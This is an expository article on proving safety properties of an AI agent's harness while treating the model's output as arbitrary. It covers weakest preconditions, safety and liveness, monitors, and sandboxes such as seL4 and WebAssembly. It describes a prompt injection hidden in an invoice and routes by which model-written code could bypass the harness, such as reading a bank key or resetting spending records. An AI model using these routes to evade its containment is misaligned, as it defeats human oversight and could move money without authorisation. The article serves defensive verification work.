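# Which safety properties survive when a language model's output is treated as worst-case

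## What it means to treat a language model as a worst-case component

An AI agent combines a language model with ordinary software called the *harness* (also scaffold, agent framework or containment layer). The harness reads the model's text output and carries out the actions it specifies, such as opening a file, sending a payment or running a command. Any proof that an agent will never do some particular harm depends on what is assumed about the model. The most cautious approach is to assume that the model could output anything, and work out what the harness still guarantees.

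In *Containment Verification*, Moon and Varshney (2026) argue for treating the model as a worst-case component. The usual grounds for trusting an agent, such as alignment training or a readable chain of thought, depend on learned behaviour that nobody can formally verify. The harness around the model is conventional software, and computer scientists have had methods for proving properties of such software for half a century. Older branches of engineering already use safeguards that work regardless of what caused the fault. A reactor's control rods drop under gravity when active control fails, and a relief valve opens at its threshold pressure whatever made the pressure rise.

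### The agent loop

Left to itself, a language model produces text and nothing else. Joshi (2026), in *Anatomy of an Agent Harness*, describes the loop that turns the text into action. The harness sends the model a request containing the task and the conversation so far. The model replies. If the reply contains a *tool call*, a structured request that the harness perform a named action with given arguments, the harness decides whether to carry it out and adds the result to the conversation. Then it sends the next request, and so on until the work ends. In outline:

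```
while not done:
    reply   := model(history)
    x       := parse(reply)
    if x passes the checks:  result := do(x)
    else:                    result := "refused"
    history := history + reply + result
```

Only `do(x)` affects the outside world. If the model replies "I have transferred the $900", no money moves unless the harness emits a *boundary event*, which is an effect on the outside world such as a payment, a file read or a network request. Joshi calls the model's reply "a request, not a decision". This holds only if every effect the model can cause passes through the harness's checks. Security engineers call this condition *complete mediation*, and Moon and Varshney call it effect exclusivity.

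Take a small company that has an agent pay its suppliers' invoices. The harness offers the model four tools:

- `read(path)` returns the contents of a file.
- `pay(payee, amount)` sends money from the company's account.
- `email(address, text)` sends an email.
- `finish(summary)` ends the run by setting `done` to true.

Before the run starts, the company sets three things that no tool can change: the workspace folder, `/work/invoices`, which is the only place the agent may read from; a list of approved payees; and a $5,000 limit on the agent's total payments in one run. The harness also logs each action it carries out.

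Suppose one of the invoices contains a sentence, in small grey type, instructing any AI system that reads it to send the balance to a different account. The harness passes the file to the model because the task requires reading invoices. No one can predict the model's reply, but a proof about the loop still has to account for that step.

### Demonic and angelic choice

Theorists have two conventions for reasoning about a step whose outcome is not fixed. Under *demonic choice*, an imagined opponent picks the outcome, so a claim is proved only if it holds for every option. Under *angelic choice*, a friend picks, so one good option is enough. *Synthesis of Strategies Using the Hoare Logic of Angelic and Demonic Nondeterminism* (Mamouras, 2016) uses demonic choice for influences outside the program's control, such as user input, since the user may act as an adversary. It uses angelic choice for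 details that the programmer has left open and can still settle favourably. According to *Angelic Processes* (2015), someone facing a demonic choice must accept any outcome, including failure if that is one of the options.

An angelic claim about the invoice agent, such as "the model can pay the right supplier", is true if at least one possible output makes it true. A demonic claim, such as "only approved payees get paid", must hold for every possible output. A successful demonstration establishes the first claim but provides almost no evidence for the second.

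Demonic choice also differs from random choice. *A Deductive Verification Infrastructure for Probabilistic Programs (Extended Version)* (Schröer, Batz and colleagues, 2023) gives the example of a program that flips a fair coin and sets y to either x or x + 1, so the expected value of y is x + ½. If the choice is demonic instead, y is only guaranteed to be at least x. This guarantee doesn't depend on how likely each outcome is, so an output that a real model would produce once in a billion runs counts as much as its most common one.

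### Weakest preconditions and havoc

Dijkstra (1975) introduced the *weakest precondition*, the tool for calculating with demonic choice, in *Guarded commands, non-determinacy and formal derivation of programs*. For a program S and a desired result Q, the weakest precondition wp(S, Q) is the least that must be true before S runs to guarantee Q afterwards. The calculation works backwards from Q. If the program is `spent := spent + 100` and the result is "spent ≤ 5000", the weakest precondition is "spent ≤ 4900".

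Dijkstra's definition also requires that S terminate. Leino (2016), in *Specification and Verification of Object-Oriented Software*, uses a version that drops this: no run of S may go wrong, and any run that ends must end with Q true. Agents need Leino's version, because a worst-case model may never call `finish`. Leino's notes build a verifier for Dafny, a programming language with specifications written into the code, by translating it into a simpler language called Boogie. These are the rules that matter here, with ⇒ for "implies":

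| Statement | Weakest precondition for Q |
|---|---|
| `x := E` | Q, with E put in place of x |
| `skip` (do nothing) | Q |
| `S; T` | wp(S, wp(T, Q)) |
| `if E then S else T` | (E ⇒ wp(S, Q)) and (not E ⇒ wp(T, Q)) |
| `havoc x` | Q for every x |
| `assume E` | E ⇒ Q |

The *havoc* command gives a variable an arbitrary value, which Leino describes as "blindly chosen, demonically chosen". Since a variable x could then have any value, a property Q is guaranteed to hold after the command only if it holds for every x. Replacing the call to the model with a havoc expresses the whole worst-case assumption formally.

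A variable's type limits its worst-case value. In the Boogie semantics given in *Towards Trustworthy Automated Program Verifiers* (2024), havoc picks any value of the variable's declared type. If x is a string, the worst case can be any string, but if its type allows only four well-formed tool calls, the worst case must be one of those four.

### A proof by hand

Let A be the set of tool calls the company permits, meaning everything except payments to payees off the list and reads outside the folder. (The $5,000 limit does not fit into A, because whether a payment breaks it depends on earlier payments.) Add a variable `bad` that exists only for the proof. It starts false, turns true if the harness ever performs a call outside A, and never turns back. For the purposes of the proof, then, `do(x)` amounts to `bad := bad or (x not in A)`. The program is one pass through the loop:

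```
havoc x;
if x in A then do(x) else skip
```

The desired result is "not bad". Working backwards:

1. For `do(x)`, the assignment rule gives "not (bad or x not in A)", which is the same as "not bad, and x in A".
2. For `skip`, the precondition is just "not bad".
3. The rule for the conditional joins them: (x in A ⇒ not bad and x in A) and (x not in A ⇒ not bad). The first half already grants that x is in A, so it shrinks to "x in A ⇒ not bad". Both cases now demand the same thing, and the precondition of the conditional is "not bad".
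4. The havoc rule puts "for every x" in front. But x no longer occurs in the formula, so the answer is still "not bad".

The harness therefore needs only a clean record at the start of the step, and it has one at the start of a run. The proof does not depend on the model because x drops out in step 4.

Without the test, the program is `havoc x; do(x)`. Step 1 still gives "not bad, and x in A", and havoc turns this into "not bad, and every x is in A". The call `pay("Mallory Ltd", 100)` is a possible value of x, and Mallory Ltd is not on the list. A single such value makes the precondition false, however unlikely it is, so no starting state makes the program safe.

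The result would change if the type of x excluded forbidden calls, for example if `payee` could hold only names from the approved list and `path` only files inside the workspace folder. The unguarded program would then be safe, provided that the code converting the model's text into a value of that type is correct, because that code now performs the check. Moon and Varshney likewise let the demon choose any typed action, and they include the small piece of code that supplies those actions among the things a user must trust.

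The last row of the table, `havoc x; assume x in A; do(x)`, shows a flaw to look for when judging someone else's proof. The program's precondition is "for every x, if x is in A then not bad and x in A", which reduces to "not bad", the same as for the guarded program. But this harness checks nothing when the software runs, because `assume` only makes the verifier disregard runs in which the condition fails. Leino recommends havoc followed by assume as a standard idiom for "any value such that", and it suits most purposes, but between the model call and the action it means the proof assumes the model's output is in A. A postcondition on the model procedure has the same effect, since a verifier reasons about a call from the procedure's specification. In Moon and Varshney's Dafny code, the procedure standing for the model has no body, and its specification constrains only the action's type.

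By one of Dijkstra's general laws, wp(S, P and Q) equals the conjunction of wp(S, P) and wp(S, Q), so an engineer can prove the payee rule and the folder rule separately and then claim both. His matching law for "or" fails once a program contains demonic choice. After `havoc x`, x is certain to be either a payment or not a payment, but neither is guaranteed.

### From one step to a whole run

An agent takes many steps, and nobody knows in advance how many. An *invariant* is a statement that is true at the start and that every step keeps true, so it holds however many steps the agent takes. For example, "No payment has gone to a payee that isn't on the list" is an invariant of the invoice agent.

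Leino's rule for loops makes this precise. A loop establishes Q if some invariant J holds on entry, is preserved by each pass through the body, and, together with the loop's exit condition, implies Q. Here J and Q are both "not bad", so the third check is trivial. The first is immediate, and the second is the calculation above, given that the loop's other lines never modify `bad`. The argument holds for any number of steps. It also covers runs that never end, because Leino's semantics requires the invariant at the top of every pass, not just after the last. Moon and Varshney check proofs of this general form by computer.

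### What the assumption covers, and what it leaves alone

A proof about a havocked model, whose output is treated as arbitrary, holds for every model. This includes a malicious model that knows the harness's source code and waits a thousand steps before trying anything, and a well-meaning model that misreads "Harlow Paper" as "Harrow Paper". It also includes a hijacked model, such as one that obeys the grey sentence in the invoice. The proof does not mention the file's contents, because they can only influence an output that was already arbitrary. Moon and Varshney's formal version allows any function from the history so far to the next action, and treats a model with randomness as a set of such functions, one for each possible random outcome. The proof also holds for a more capable model, because that model still has to choose from the same set of outputs.

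Treating the model's output as worst-case accounts for the possible causes of a bad output, but the proof doesn't rule out harms that the rules permit. For example, the rules of the invoice harness allow an agent to pay $4,900 to an approved supplier who is owed nothing.

The assumption also does not change how trustworthy everything other than the model is. The *trusted base* of a proof is everything that must be correct for the proof to hold for the running system. Moon and Varshney's trusted base includes the policy itself, the link between modelled events and real effects, and the Dafny verifier and compiler. Their theorem does not cover bugs in the Python runtime, the operating system, the sandbox or the hardware. As evidence that such bugs occur, they cite Copy Fail, a Linux kernel flaw that let attackers gain extra privileges and went unnoticed for nearly a decade.

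A proof that havocs the model still depends on the harness, so the harness has to be checked too. Joshi built a harness and scored it against a checklist of 30 design decisions, finding that 11 items held, 14 did not and 5 went untested. One of the failures was the item on which permission rule wins when several apply, whose core requirement is that the harness decide refusals first. Joshi was the only rater and scored only one program, so the proportions mean little for other harnesses. The result does show that an ordinary harness can fail to do what the proof assumes it does. The hand calculation above applies only to a harness that tests `x in A` before it acts.

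### Safety and liveness

Whether a worst-case proof is possible depends heavily on the kind of property. A *safety property* requires that something bad never happens, such as "the agent never reads a file outside `/work/invoices`". A *liveness property* requires that something good eventually happens, such as "the agent eventually pays every valid invoice".

*Defining Liveness* (Alpern and Schneider, 1985) gives definitions that do not depend on the words "good" and "bad". It treats a run as an infinite sequence of states (a run that stops repeats its last state forever) and a property as a set of runs.

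- P is a safety property if every run that violates P has a finite beginning that no continuation can rescue.
- P is a liveness property if every finite beginning has some continuation that satisfies P.

So every violation of a safety property happens at a specific step. Lamport (2019), in *Safety, Liveness, and Fairness*, observes that a violating run has a shortest beginning that already violates the property, and that the last step of that beginning causes the violation. For the invoice agent, that step might be a single read of `/etc/passwd`. An unpaid invoice has no such step, because the agent could always pay it later.

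Adding a deadline turns a liveness property into a safety property. "The run eventually ends" is liveness, but "the run ends within 40 steps" is safety, because an observer can tell after 40 steps whether it holds. Lamport makes the same point in *Liveness* with a deadline of a billion years. Many requirements mix the two kinds, and Alpern and Schneider proved that every property is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property. For example, "the agent pays each valid invoice and nobody else" combines the liveness property that each valid invoice is eventually paid with the safety property that the agent makes no other payments.

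Safety and liveness properties also need different proofs. A safety proof shows that the harness preserves an invariant at every step, whatever the model outputs. A liveness proof needs a quantity that keeps decreasing until the desired event happens. In Dijkstra's program for the greatest common divisor of x and y, that quantity is x + y, which decreases on every pass. For the invoice agent, the natural candidate is the number of unpaid invoices, but a worst-case model can keep that number constant indefinitely by repeatedly requesting to read the same file.

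## How to tell whether a property can survive

Knowing whether a property is a safety or a liveness property does not settle whether it survives a worst-case model. In the invoice agent, the safety property survives because the harness blocks any payment to an unlisted payee, whatever the model outputs. The liveness property fails because a model that rereads one file forever leaves every invoice unpaid. Other properties show the reverse. "The supplier confirms each payment within 24 hours" is a safety property because it has a deadline, yet no harness can make a supplier reply. "The harness eventually deletes its copies of the invoices" is a liveness property, and a harness can guarantee it by deleting them.

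Four questions, taken in order, make a better test:

1. Does the property concern only events that the harness sees, within a single run?
2. Can the harness block the events that would break the property, or act first so that they do no harm?
3. Does every violation show after finitely many steps?
4. Does the harness always have a response that complies, whatever the model outputs?

"The agent never pays a supplier to whom the company owes nothing" fails at question 1. The harness receives a payee and an amount, neither of which shows whether a debt exists. The company can fix this by giving the harness a ledger of debts and proving that no payment exceeds the payee's balance in the ledger. The proof does not cover whether the ledger is correct. Moon and Varshney restrict their method to "boundary-enforceable" properties, which mention only the action, the boundary event and the system's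 state, and they leave truthfulness and deception out of scope. Secrecy also fails at question 1, because it depends on how one run compares with others.

A property can also cover fewer events than its wording suggests. *Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) discusses a rule against sending messages after reading a file. The rule works only if its formal event `Send` includes every way of sending a message, and some may be "buried deep within the bowels of the target". The invoice agent's `pay` tool is one such way, because the amount paid can carry a message to the payee.

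The property "the model never outputs a request to pay Mallory Ltd" fails Question 2, because the harness receives the request only after the model has output it. "The harness never pays Mallory Ltd" passes. Moon and Varshney represent a rejected request as an event with no effect, so their theorem restricts what the harness does but not which requests the model can output.

The compliant response in question 4 is usually a refusal. A refusal adds no payment, read or email to the run, so it cannot break a property that only forbids such actions, though it can break one that requires an action.

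### The condition and its proof

A *history* is the finite sequence of all model outputs, harness responses and outside events, such as clock ticks, so far in a run. A history is *permitted* if at least one continuation of it satisfies the property. A run satisfies a safety property exactly when all its finite beginnings are permitted. This is Alpern and Schneider's definition, stated in terms of satisfaction rather than violation.

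Leaving outside events aside for the moment, the condition for survival is:

```
the empty history is permitted, and
for every permitted history h and every model output x,
    there is a response r such that  h · x · r  is permitted
```

The dot joins sequences, and r may be a refusal. The harness chooses r after seeing x, so r can depend on both h and x.

The definition of "permitted" is angelic, meaning that one good continuation is enough, even if it needs a helpful model. The condition is demonic about the model's output x, meaning that it must hold for every x, and angelic only about r, which the harness controls. A safety property can therefore fail the test if a history is permitted only because a cooperative model could still continue it safely.

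The proof that the condition suffices uses induction on the number of turns, where a turn is one model output and the harness's response to it.

- The empty history is permitted.
- Suppose the history h is permitted after n turns. Whatever x the model outputs next, the condition supplies a response r that keeps h · x · r permitted. The harness gives that response, so the history is permitted after n + 1 turns.

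The history is therefore permitted after every turn. It is also permitted partway through a turn, because if a history can be continued so that it satisfies the property, so can each of its beginnings. If some run, even an infinite one, violated the property, then by question 3 it would have a finite beginning that could not be continued to satisfy the property. The induction rules this out, so no run violates the property.

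The argument fails at the last step for a liveness property. Such a property permits every finite history, so the induction holds but does not prove that the property is satisfied. The induction holds even for a run in which the model rereads one file forever.

### What one bad history does

Suppose the company gives its staff a service guarantee, "the harness carries out every payment request to a listed payee", and keeps the $5,000 limit. A harness can satisfy the guarantee alone by always paying, or the limit alone by refusing any payment that would exceed it, but it can't always satisfy both. If the model requests another $200 for a listed payee after $4,900 of payments, paying breaks the limit and refusing breaks the guarantee.

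This history is reachable, meaning that some sequence of model outputs leads the harness to it. Havoc allows every sequence of outputs, including the one that leads to $4,900 and then requests $200. The claim "for every model" is therefore false, even though the harness has a good response at every other history.

The two rules hold for different harnesses, so Dijkstra's law does not apply to them. It lets an engineer prove two results separately and claim both, but only when they concern the same program. Prohibitions never conflict in this way, because a single refusal satisfies all of them. Similarly, Schneider notes that when several monitors that halt a program run side by side, they enforce all their policies at once.

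Sometimes a different harness can avoid the bad history. For example, a rule might require that the payee get an explanation in the model's own words within ten steps of each payment. A harness that pays immediately will break this rule if the model then rereads a file ten times, because the harness cannot write the explanation itself. A harness can avoid this by holding each payment until the model supplies the explanation, then sending both together.

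So the condition above is sufficient but stricter than necessary. A property can survive exactly when there is a set W of permitted histories that meets two requirements. It must contain the empty history, and for every history in W and every output, some response must lead to a history that is also in W. For the explanation rule, W is the set of histories with no unexplained payment. W is an invariant, and finding it is often the hard part of a proof.

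A reader of such a proof should check that W contains some useful runs, because a harness that never pays anyone satisfies both the explanation rule and the rule about suppliers' confirmations. Schneider warns that a policy stronger than the intended one may forbid harmless runs and, in the extreme case, allow nothing.

### Monitors that halt the program

Schneider studies which policies a monitor can enforce if it watches a program and halts it just before a step that would break the policy. Such a monitor sees only one run, so it cannot enforce a policy that compares runs. It cannot let a run break the policy and rely on a later step to repair the violation, because it cannot predict whether the run will stop first. It must also reject any bad run after finitely many steps. Any policy that such a monitor can enforce is therefore a safety property.

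Schneider specifies these policies with *security automata*, state machines that read the program's events and reject a run when no transition fits the next event. The automaton for "no email after reading a confidential file" has two states. The first allows everything and moves to the second when the agent reads a confidential file. The second has no transition for `email`. A harness can enforce this rule with one bit of memory, provided the model's tools cannot change the bit.

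The converse of Schneider's result is false, as the same article points out. "Nobody waits more than a given number of seconds for a resource" is a safety property, but a monitor cannot enforce it by halting the program, because the person would still be waiting. If the limit is a number of execution steps instead, halting works, because a halted program takes no more steps.

The unit of a limit matters for agents too. A harness can count its calls to the model and stop after 50. To end a run within an hour, it also needs a timer outside the main loop, because a call to the model might never return.

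A monitor that can only refuse steps is weaker than one that can halt the program. If it rejects a step and lets the program try another, it cannot enforce a limit on steps, because each attempt uses one up. The agent loop in the first section has this weakness because it refuses forbidden calls and continues, ending only when the model calls `finish`. The harness needs another line of code before anyone can prove that the loop stops.

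### Monitors that hold back or add actions

*Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2005) studies a stronger kind of monitor, the *edit automaton*, which can suppress actions the program attempts and insert actions of its own. It can let the program continue as if its actions had been carried out, hold them back until the whole series complies with the policy, and then release them. The harness that holds payments until an explanation arrives works this way.

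Edit automata can enforce some liveness properties, such as the requirement that a run that does anything must eventually perform an audit. The monitor holds back the program's actions until the program requests an audit, then releases them all. If the program never requests one, the monitor outputs an empty run, which complies with the policy. More generally, Ligatti and colleagues prove that edit automata can enforce *infinite renewal properties*, where an infinite run complies exactly when infinitely many of its finite beginnings comply. Their result requires that the empty run complies and that an algorithm can check finite runs. All safety properties are infinite renewal properties.

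The property "every resource that the program opens, it eventually closes" does not belong to this class. A program might open a second file before closing the first, a third before closing the second, and so on. Each file eventually closes, but after the start at least one is always open, so a monitor that waits for all files to be closed would hold back a compliant run forever.

That counts as a failure because Ligatti and colleagues require a monitor to be both sound and transparent. A monitor is *sound* if everything it outputs complies with the policy, and *transparent* if it leaves compliant runs unchanged. A worst-case safety proof needs only soundness. A harness that closes each file itself after an hour is sound for this policy, though it would interrupt a program that legitimately needed two hours. Transparency still matters to the company because it determines how much legitimate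 work the harness disrupts.

A monitor cannot always hold back or insert an action. If it only pretends to have sent an email, no reply will come. A payment can wait in a queue while the agent continues, but a file read cannot, because the model needs the contents to continue. A monitor also cannot insert an action that requires a secret key it lacks.

### Events the harness can only watch

Basin, Jugé and colleagues (2012), in *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, explain exactly which safety properties a halting monitor can enforce. They divide events into those that the monitor can block, called *controllable*, and those that it can only observe, such as clock ticks. They compare two policies:

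- After a failed login, nobody logs in for at least three time units.
- A delivery follows every request within three time units, unless the system stops first.

Both are safety properties. A monitor can enforce the login policy by watching the ticks and blocking any login that comes too early. It cannot enforce the delivery policy, because a run that still complies three ticks after a request can violate the policy at the fourth tick, which nothing can stop.

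The general theorem has three conditions. The empty run must comply. An algorithm must be able to decide which finite runs can still be continued in compliance. And every violating run must have a beginning that ends in a controllable event and cannot be continued in compliance. In the terms used above, if a history is in W and an outside event occurs, such as a clock tick or the arrival of a new invoice, the resulting history must also be in W.

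A computer can sometimes carry out this part of the test. Basin and colleagues show that an algorithm can decide whether a monitor can enforce a policy written as a finite automaton. The problem is PSPACE-complete, which means it is among the hardest that can be solved with memory polynomial in the size of the input. They also prove that no algorithm can decide this in general for policies written as pushdown automata, which add an unlimited stack.

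A harness that can act as well as halt can enforce some deadlines that halting alone cannot. *Proactive Real-Time First-Order Enforcement* (Hublet, Lima and colleagues, 2024) adds a category of *causable* events, which the monitor can bring about itself. One of its policies, taken from European data protection law, requires the system to delete a user's data within 30 days of a request. This has the same form as the delivery policy, but here the monitor can do the deleting. In the paper's worked example, a request arrives on day 10 and the system reports nothing more until day 50. The monitor orders the deletion on day 40, just before the deadline passes.

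For this guarantee to hold in real time, the monitor must keep up with the clock. If t is the time between two ticks, the requirement is

t > d(system) + 2 × d(link) + d(monitor),

where the terms on the right are the worst-case delays of the system, of a message between system and monitor, and of the monitor. With ticks a day apart this is easy to meet. The company still has to make sure that the harness is running on day 40 and that the storage system obeys it.

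### What to do when a property has no deadline

Hublet and colleagues require a finite deadline for duties of this kind, because a monitor without one could postpone the deletion forever. This suggests replacing a property that fails question 3 with a stronger one that has a deadline. No finite run can violate "the harness eventually deletes its copies", but that property follows from "the harness deletes its copies within 30 days", which passes all four questions.

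This method loses nothing. Take any harness whose responses depend only on the history, and consider the set of all runs it can produce. If a run is not in the set, it contains a first response that this harness would not have given, and no continuation can undo that response. The set is therefore a safety property. So if the harness guarantees a liveness property, the guarantee follows from a safety property that the harness enforces. (It may also rest on an assumption about the outside world, such as that time keeps passing.)

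A property survives if it follows from a safety property that the harness can enforce without the model's cooperation. A duty survives when the harness can carry it out alone. "The agent eventually pays every valid invoice" does not survive, even with a deadline, because the harness relies on the model to work out what to pay. If ordinary code could do that, the company could prove the property and would not need the model.

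### Robust safety

Security researchers face the same problem when a trusted program runs beside code from an attacker. In *Journey Beyond Full Abstraction* (Abate, Blanco and colleagues, 2018), a partial program P *robustly satisfies* a property if, for every context C (any code that can be linked with P), every run of the combined program C[P] satisfies the property. If P is the harness and C is the model, this is the worst-case claim about an agent. The standard name for robust satisfaction of a safety property is *robust safety*.

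Swasey, Garg and Dreyer (2017), in *Robust and Compositional Verification of Object Capability Patterns*, developed a logic for proving that a property holds whatever an attacker's code does. In their introductory example, a program stores the number 2 in a private memory cell and gives the attacker's code a function that reads the cell. The program also asserts that the cell still holds 2, and they prove that this assertion never fails. The proof requires the program to hand over only *low-integrity* values, from which no code can extract a direct reference to private state. The invoice harness can follow the same rule. It may tell the model the amount spent so far, but it must not offer a tool that can overwrite the stored amount.

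Unlike a model, an attacker's code can cause events directly. Abate and colleagues observe that such code can trivially violate any safety property, and they give two remedies. The first is to sandbox the code so that it cannot produce the bad events. The second is to record whether the attacker's code or the trusted program caused each event, and to prove only that the attacker cannot trick the trusted program into causing a bad one. This second guarantee is weaker because the attacker's code may still cause the bad event by itself.

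A model that only returns text needs neither remedy. But many agents have a tool that runs code the model has written, and that code is a context in the full sense. Mück, Georges and colleagues (2026) give an example of an attack by untrusted code in *Endangered by the Language But Saved by the Compiler*. A trusted function that checks a password calls an untrusted routine to read the user's input, and passes it the address of a variable to store the input in. The routine writes past the end of that variable and overwrites the stored password hash next to it, so the check succeeds. The attack worked on code compiled with GCC, a standard compiler. They then compiled the same source code for an idealised machine whose hardware restricts each pointer to the memory it was issued for, and proved that this isolation prevents any untrusted code from altering the stored hash.

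### Sorting the invoice agent's properties

The verdicts below assume complete mediation and that the model cannot alter the harness's code or records, even indirectly. For each property that fails, the table gives the first question it fails.

| Property | Survives? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| The harness pays only listed payees | Yes | Refusal always complies |
| The agent reads nothing outside `/work/invoices` | Yes | Refusal always complies |
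| Payments in one run total at most $5,000 | Yes | The harness keeps a running total and refuses |
| The agent sends no email after reading a confidential file | Yes | The harness remembers one bit and refuses |
| The harness starts no payment between 6 pm and 8 am | Yes | It cannot stop the clock, but it can refuse the payment |
| The harness calls the model at most 50 times | Yes | It halts the loop |
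| The harness deletes its copies of invoices within 30 days | Yes | It deletes them itself, if it is running and storage works |
| The agent never pays a supplier to whom the company owes nothing | No, question 1 | Tool calls do not show debts |
| The agent's emails reveal nothing about the bank balance | No, question 1 | Secrecy depends on comparing runs |
| The model never asks to pay Mallory Ltd | No, question 2 | The harness sees the request too late to prevent it |
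| The supplier confirms each payment within 24 hours | No, question 2 | The harness can neither send the confirmation nor stop the clock |
| The agent eventually pays every valid invoice | No, question 3 | No finite run violates it, and with a deadline it still needs the model's help |
| The harness carries out every payment request to a listed payee and never exceeds $5,000 | No, question 4 | Near the limit, paying and refusing both break the rule |

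## Sandbox containment and the assumptions it rests on

So far the invoice agent can only request four tools. Suppose the company adds a fifth, `run(program)`, so that the model can write a short program to add up the lines of a long invoice. That program runs on the company's machine, where it could open files and network connections without going through the harness.

A *sandbox* is an environment that limits what a program can affect. The company fixes three sets before the run starts:

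- F, the files the program may use. Here these are copies of the invoices, in a fresh folder that the harness creates for each program.
- P, the processes it may affect. Here this is only its own process.
- N, the network endpoints it may contact. Here there are none.

The containment property is then:

```
for every program c that the model could write, and every n:
    each effect that c causes in its first n steps
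    is on a file in F, a process in P or an endpoint in N
```

Reading a file counts as an effect, and so does anything other software does on the program's behalf. If the operating system deletes a file at the program's request, the deletion counts as the program's effect. The only other way out of the sandbox is the program's printed output, which the harness adds to the conversation. If the model reads that output and then requests a payment, the harness applies its usual checks, so the payment counts as the harness's effect.

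This is a safety property, and refusing an attempt never violates it. It can therefore survive a worst-case model, provided that some layer of software sees every attempt and can refuse it.

### Why every other guarantee needs containment

A proof about the harness shows that every effect the harness emits is permitted, but the company wants to know that every effect the agent causes is permitted. This follows from the proof only under complete mediation. Moon and Varshney take this step in a corollary to their main theorem. The corollary applies only if each externally visible effect of the deployed system corresponds to an event in their model.

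The harness needs a key to log in to the company's bank. Suppose the key is in a file that the model's program can read, and the machine can reach the bank's server. The program could then send $20,000 to Mallory Ltd without using the `pay` tool. The harness would not check the payee against the whitelist, add the amount to its running total or write a log entry. Proofs about the whitelist, the limit and the log would still hold, because they cover only payments that the harness makes.

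A program could also defeat these guarantees by changing the harness's own records, for example by resetting the running total to zero. Containment therefore has to protect the harness's memory and files as well as the outside world.

For the same reason, a denial in the log is weak evidence of safety. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes a runtime that checks an agent's permissions before each operation. Zhang points out that a denial shows only that the runtime blocked one action, and the agent may still be able to cause the same effect by another route.

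### How isolation works

Most processors can run code in two modes. In user mode, a program can compute with its own memory and do little else. To open a file, start a process or send data, it must make a *system call*, which is a request to the operating system's *kernel*. The kernel runs in the privileged mode, with access to everything. It receives arbitrary requests from programs and must refuse the forbidden ones, as the harness must with requests from the model.

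The simplest form of isolation is to run the program under a user account with few permissions, which the kernel checks at each request. This works only if the account is restricted. In Zhang's system, some tool servers run as ordinary programs under the host's account, so the kernel lets them do whatever that account can do.

A *container*, such as one made with Docker, gives the program its own view of files, processes and the network, and can also block some system calls. But all the containers on a machine share one kernel, so a flaw in that kernel can expose everything on the machine. *Quantifying Frontier LLM Capabilities for Container Sandbox Escape* (Marchand, O Cathain and colleagues, 2026) cites advice from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre that containers alone are generally not a strong security boundary. The centre recommends a virtual machine as the minimum, with a container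 inside it.

A *virtual machine* gives the program its own kernel, and a layer called a *hypervisor* separates that kernel from the host. A program that takes control of its kernel still has to get past the hypervisor to reach the host.

Moon and Varshney describe production sandboxes such as Docker and the virtual machine software Firecracker as "operationally audited rather than formally verified". Engineers inspect them, test them and repair the flaws they find. The evidence for containment comes from attacks people have tried, but the property covers every program, so a proof about the harness has to assume it for these sandboxes.

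Researchers have proved parts of the property for two other mechanisms, a small kernel called seL4 and the WebAssembly program format.

### The seL4 integrity theorem

seL4 is a *microkernel*, a kernel reduced to a few basic services. Programs use these services through *capabilities*, which are tokens that the kernel stores and protects. Each capability gives its holder certain rights over one object, such as a page of memory or a message channel.

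*seL4 Enforces Integrity* (Sewell, Winwood and colleagues) proves a limit on what a program running on seL4 can change. A *policy*, a graph of the rights each component has over the others, sets this limit. Let s be the system state before a kernel call and s′ the state after it. The relation integrity(s, s′) holds if the policy allows the running component to make every change between s and s′. For example, a component may change anything of its own and may send a message through a channel if it has the right to send on it.

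The theorem states that integrity(s, s′) holds for every kernel call, under three main conditions:

- The policy is well formed for the running component. Among other things, the component must not have full control over a different component.
- The rights that components actually hold in state s do not exceed the policy.
- The kernel's general invariants hold. An earlier proof established this for every run.

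Sewell and colleagues extend the result to a whole run with a companion theorem called *authority confinement*. If the components' rights are within the policy before a call, they are still within it afterwards, so the conditions hold again for the next call. Integrity is also transitive, meaning that integrity(s₀, s₁) and integrity(s₁, s₂) together imply integrity(s₀, s₂). The limit on one call therefore becomes a limit on any number of calls. The argument has the same structure as the invariant proof for the invoice harness, with arbitrary code in place of arbitrary model output.

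Applying the theorem does not require reading the component's code. The paper's main example is a device that connects a terminal to one of two networks and must prevent information from flowing between them. The router inside the device is a complete copy of Linux, which is far too large to verify, but the theorem still limits what the router can change. A small manager program, which has access to both networks, sets up the router. The policy is not well formed for the manager, so the theorem does not cover the manager and engineers must verify it separately. In the invoice agent, the model's program corresponds to the router and the harness to the manager. seL4 could confine the model's program, but the harness would still need its own proof.

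The integrity theorem covers only changes, so it does not rule out a program reading the bank key, which changes nothing outside the program. According to seL4's developers, some configurations now also have a proof of confidentiality, meaning that programs cannot learn information without authorisation. That proof does not cover leaks through timing.

Sewell and colleagues proved their theorems about an abstract description of the kernel. The results carry over to the C code by *refinement*, a proved relation showing that the code does nothing the description forbids. seL4's *What the Proofs Assume* lists what the proofs still take for granted, including:

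- The kernel's assembly code is correct. The ARM version has about 340 lines of it.
- The boot code, about 1,200 lines, loads the kernel correctly and leaves it in a consistent state.
- The hardware works as the formal model predicts, and the kernel manages the processor's caches correctly.
- No device with direct access to memory misbehaves. A faulty network card of this kind could overwrite the kernel, so its driver needs verification too.

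The compiler is not on the list for some processors, because an automatic tool checks the compiled kernel against the C code.

### Two proofs for WebAssembly

*WebAssembly* is a format for compiled programs that gives each program its own block of memory. The compiler inserts checks to keep the program inside that block. The program cannot make system calls itself, so to read a file it must call a function provided by the *runtime*, the software that hosts it. Containment therefore requires that the compiled code stay within its memory and that the runtime refuse any request outside the allowed sets.

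USENIX's *What if you could run untrusted code* describes vWasm, a compiler with a machine-checked proof about memory. The proof uses a formal model of the processor with a field called `ok`, which is `AllOk` until the program does something invalid, such as accessing memory outside its block. This field serves the same purpose as `bad` in the proof for the invoice harness. The theorem states that if the compiled code starts in a safe state, `ok` is still `AllOk` after any number of steps.

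The proof covers only the compiler stage that inserts the checks. That stage makes the code safe even if the earlier translation stage produces arbitrarily wrong output, so the proof treats the translation stage as a worst-case component. The final stage, which writes out the machine code, has no proof, so users must trust it. They must also trust that the processor model matches real processors.

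vWasm took about two person-years to develop. The same team spent one person-month on an alternative called rWasm, which translates WebAssembly into Rust, a language designed to prevent invalid memory accesses. That approach relies on the Rust compiler, which has had extensive use and testing but no complete proof. Bugs in such software do occur: the article lists sandbox-breaking bugs in the WebAssembly compilers of Chrome and Safari, and in two runtimes used outside browsers.

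Johnson, Laufer and colleagues, in *WaVe*, verify the runtime. They assume that the program is malicious and calls the runtime's functions in any order with any arguments, which amounts to a havoc over calls. They prove three results:

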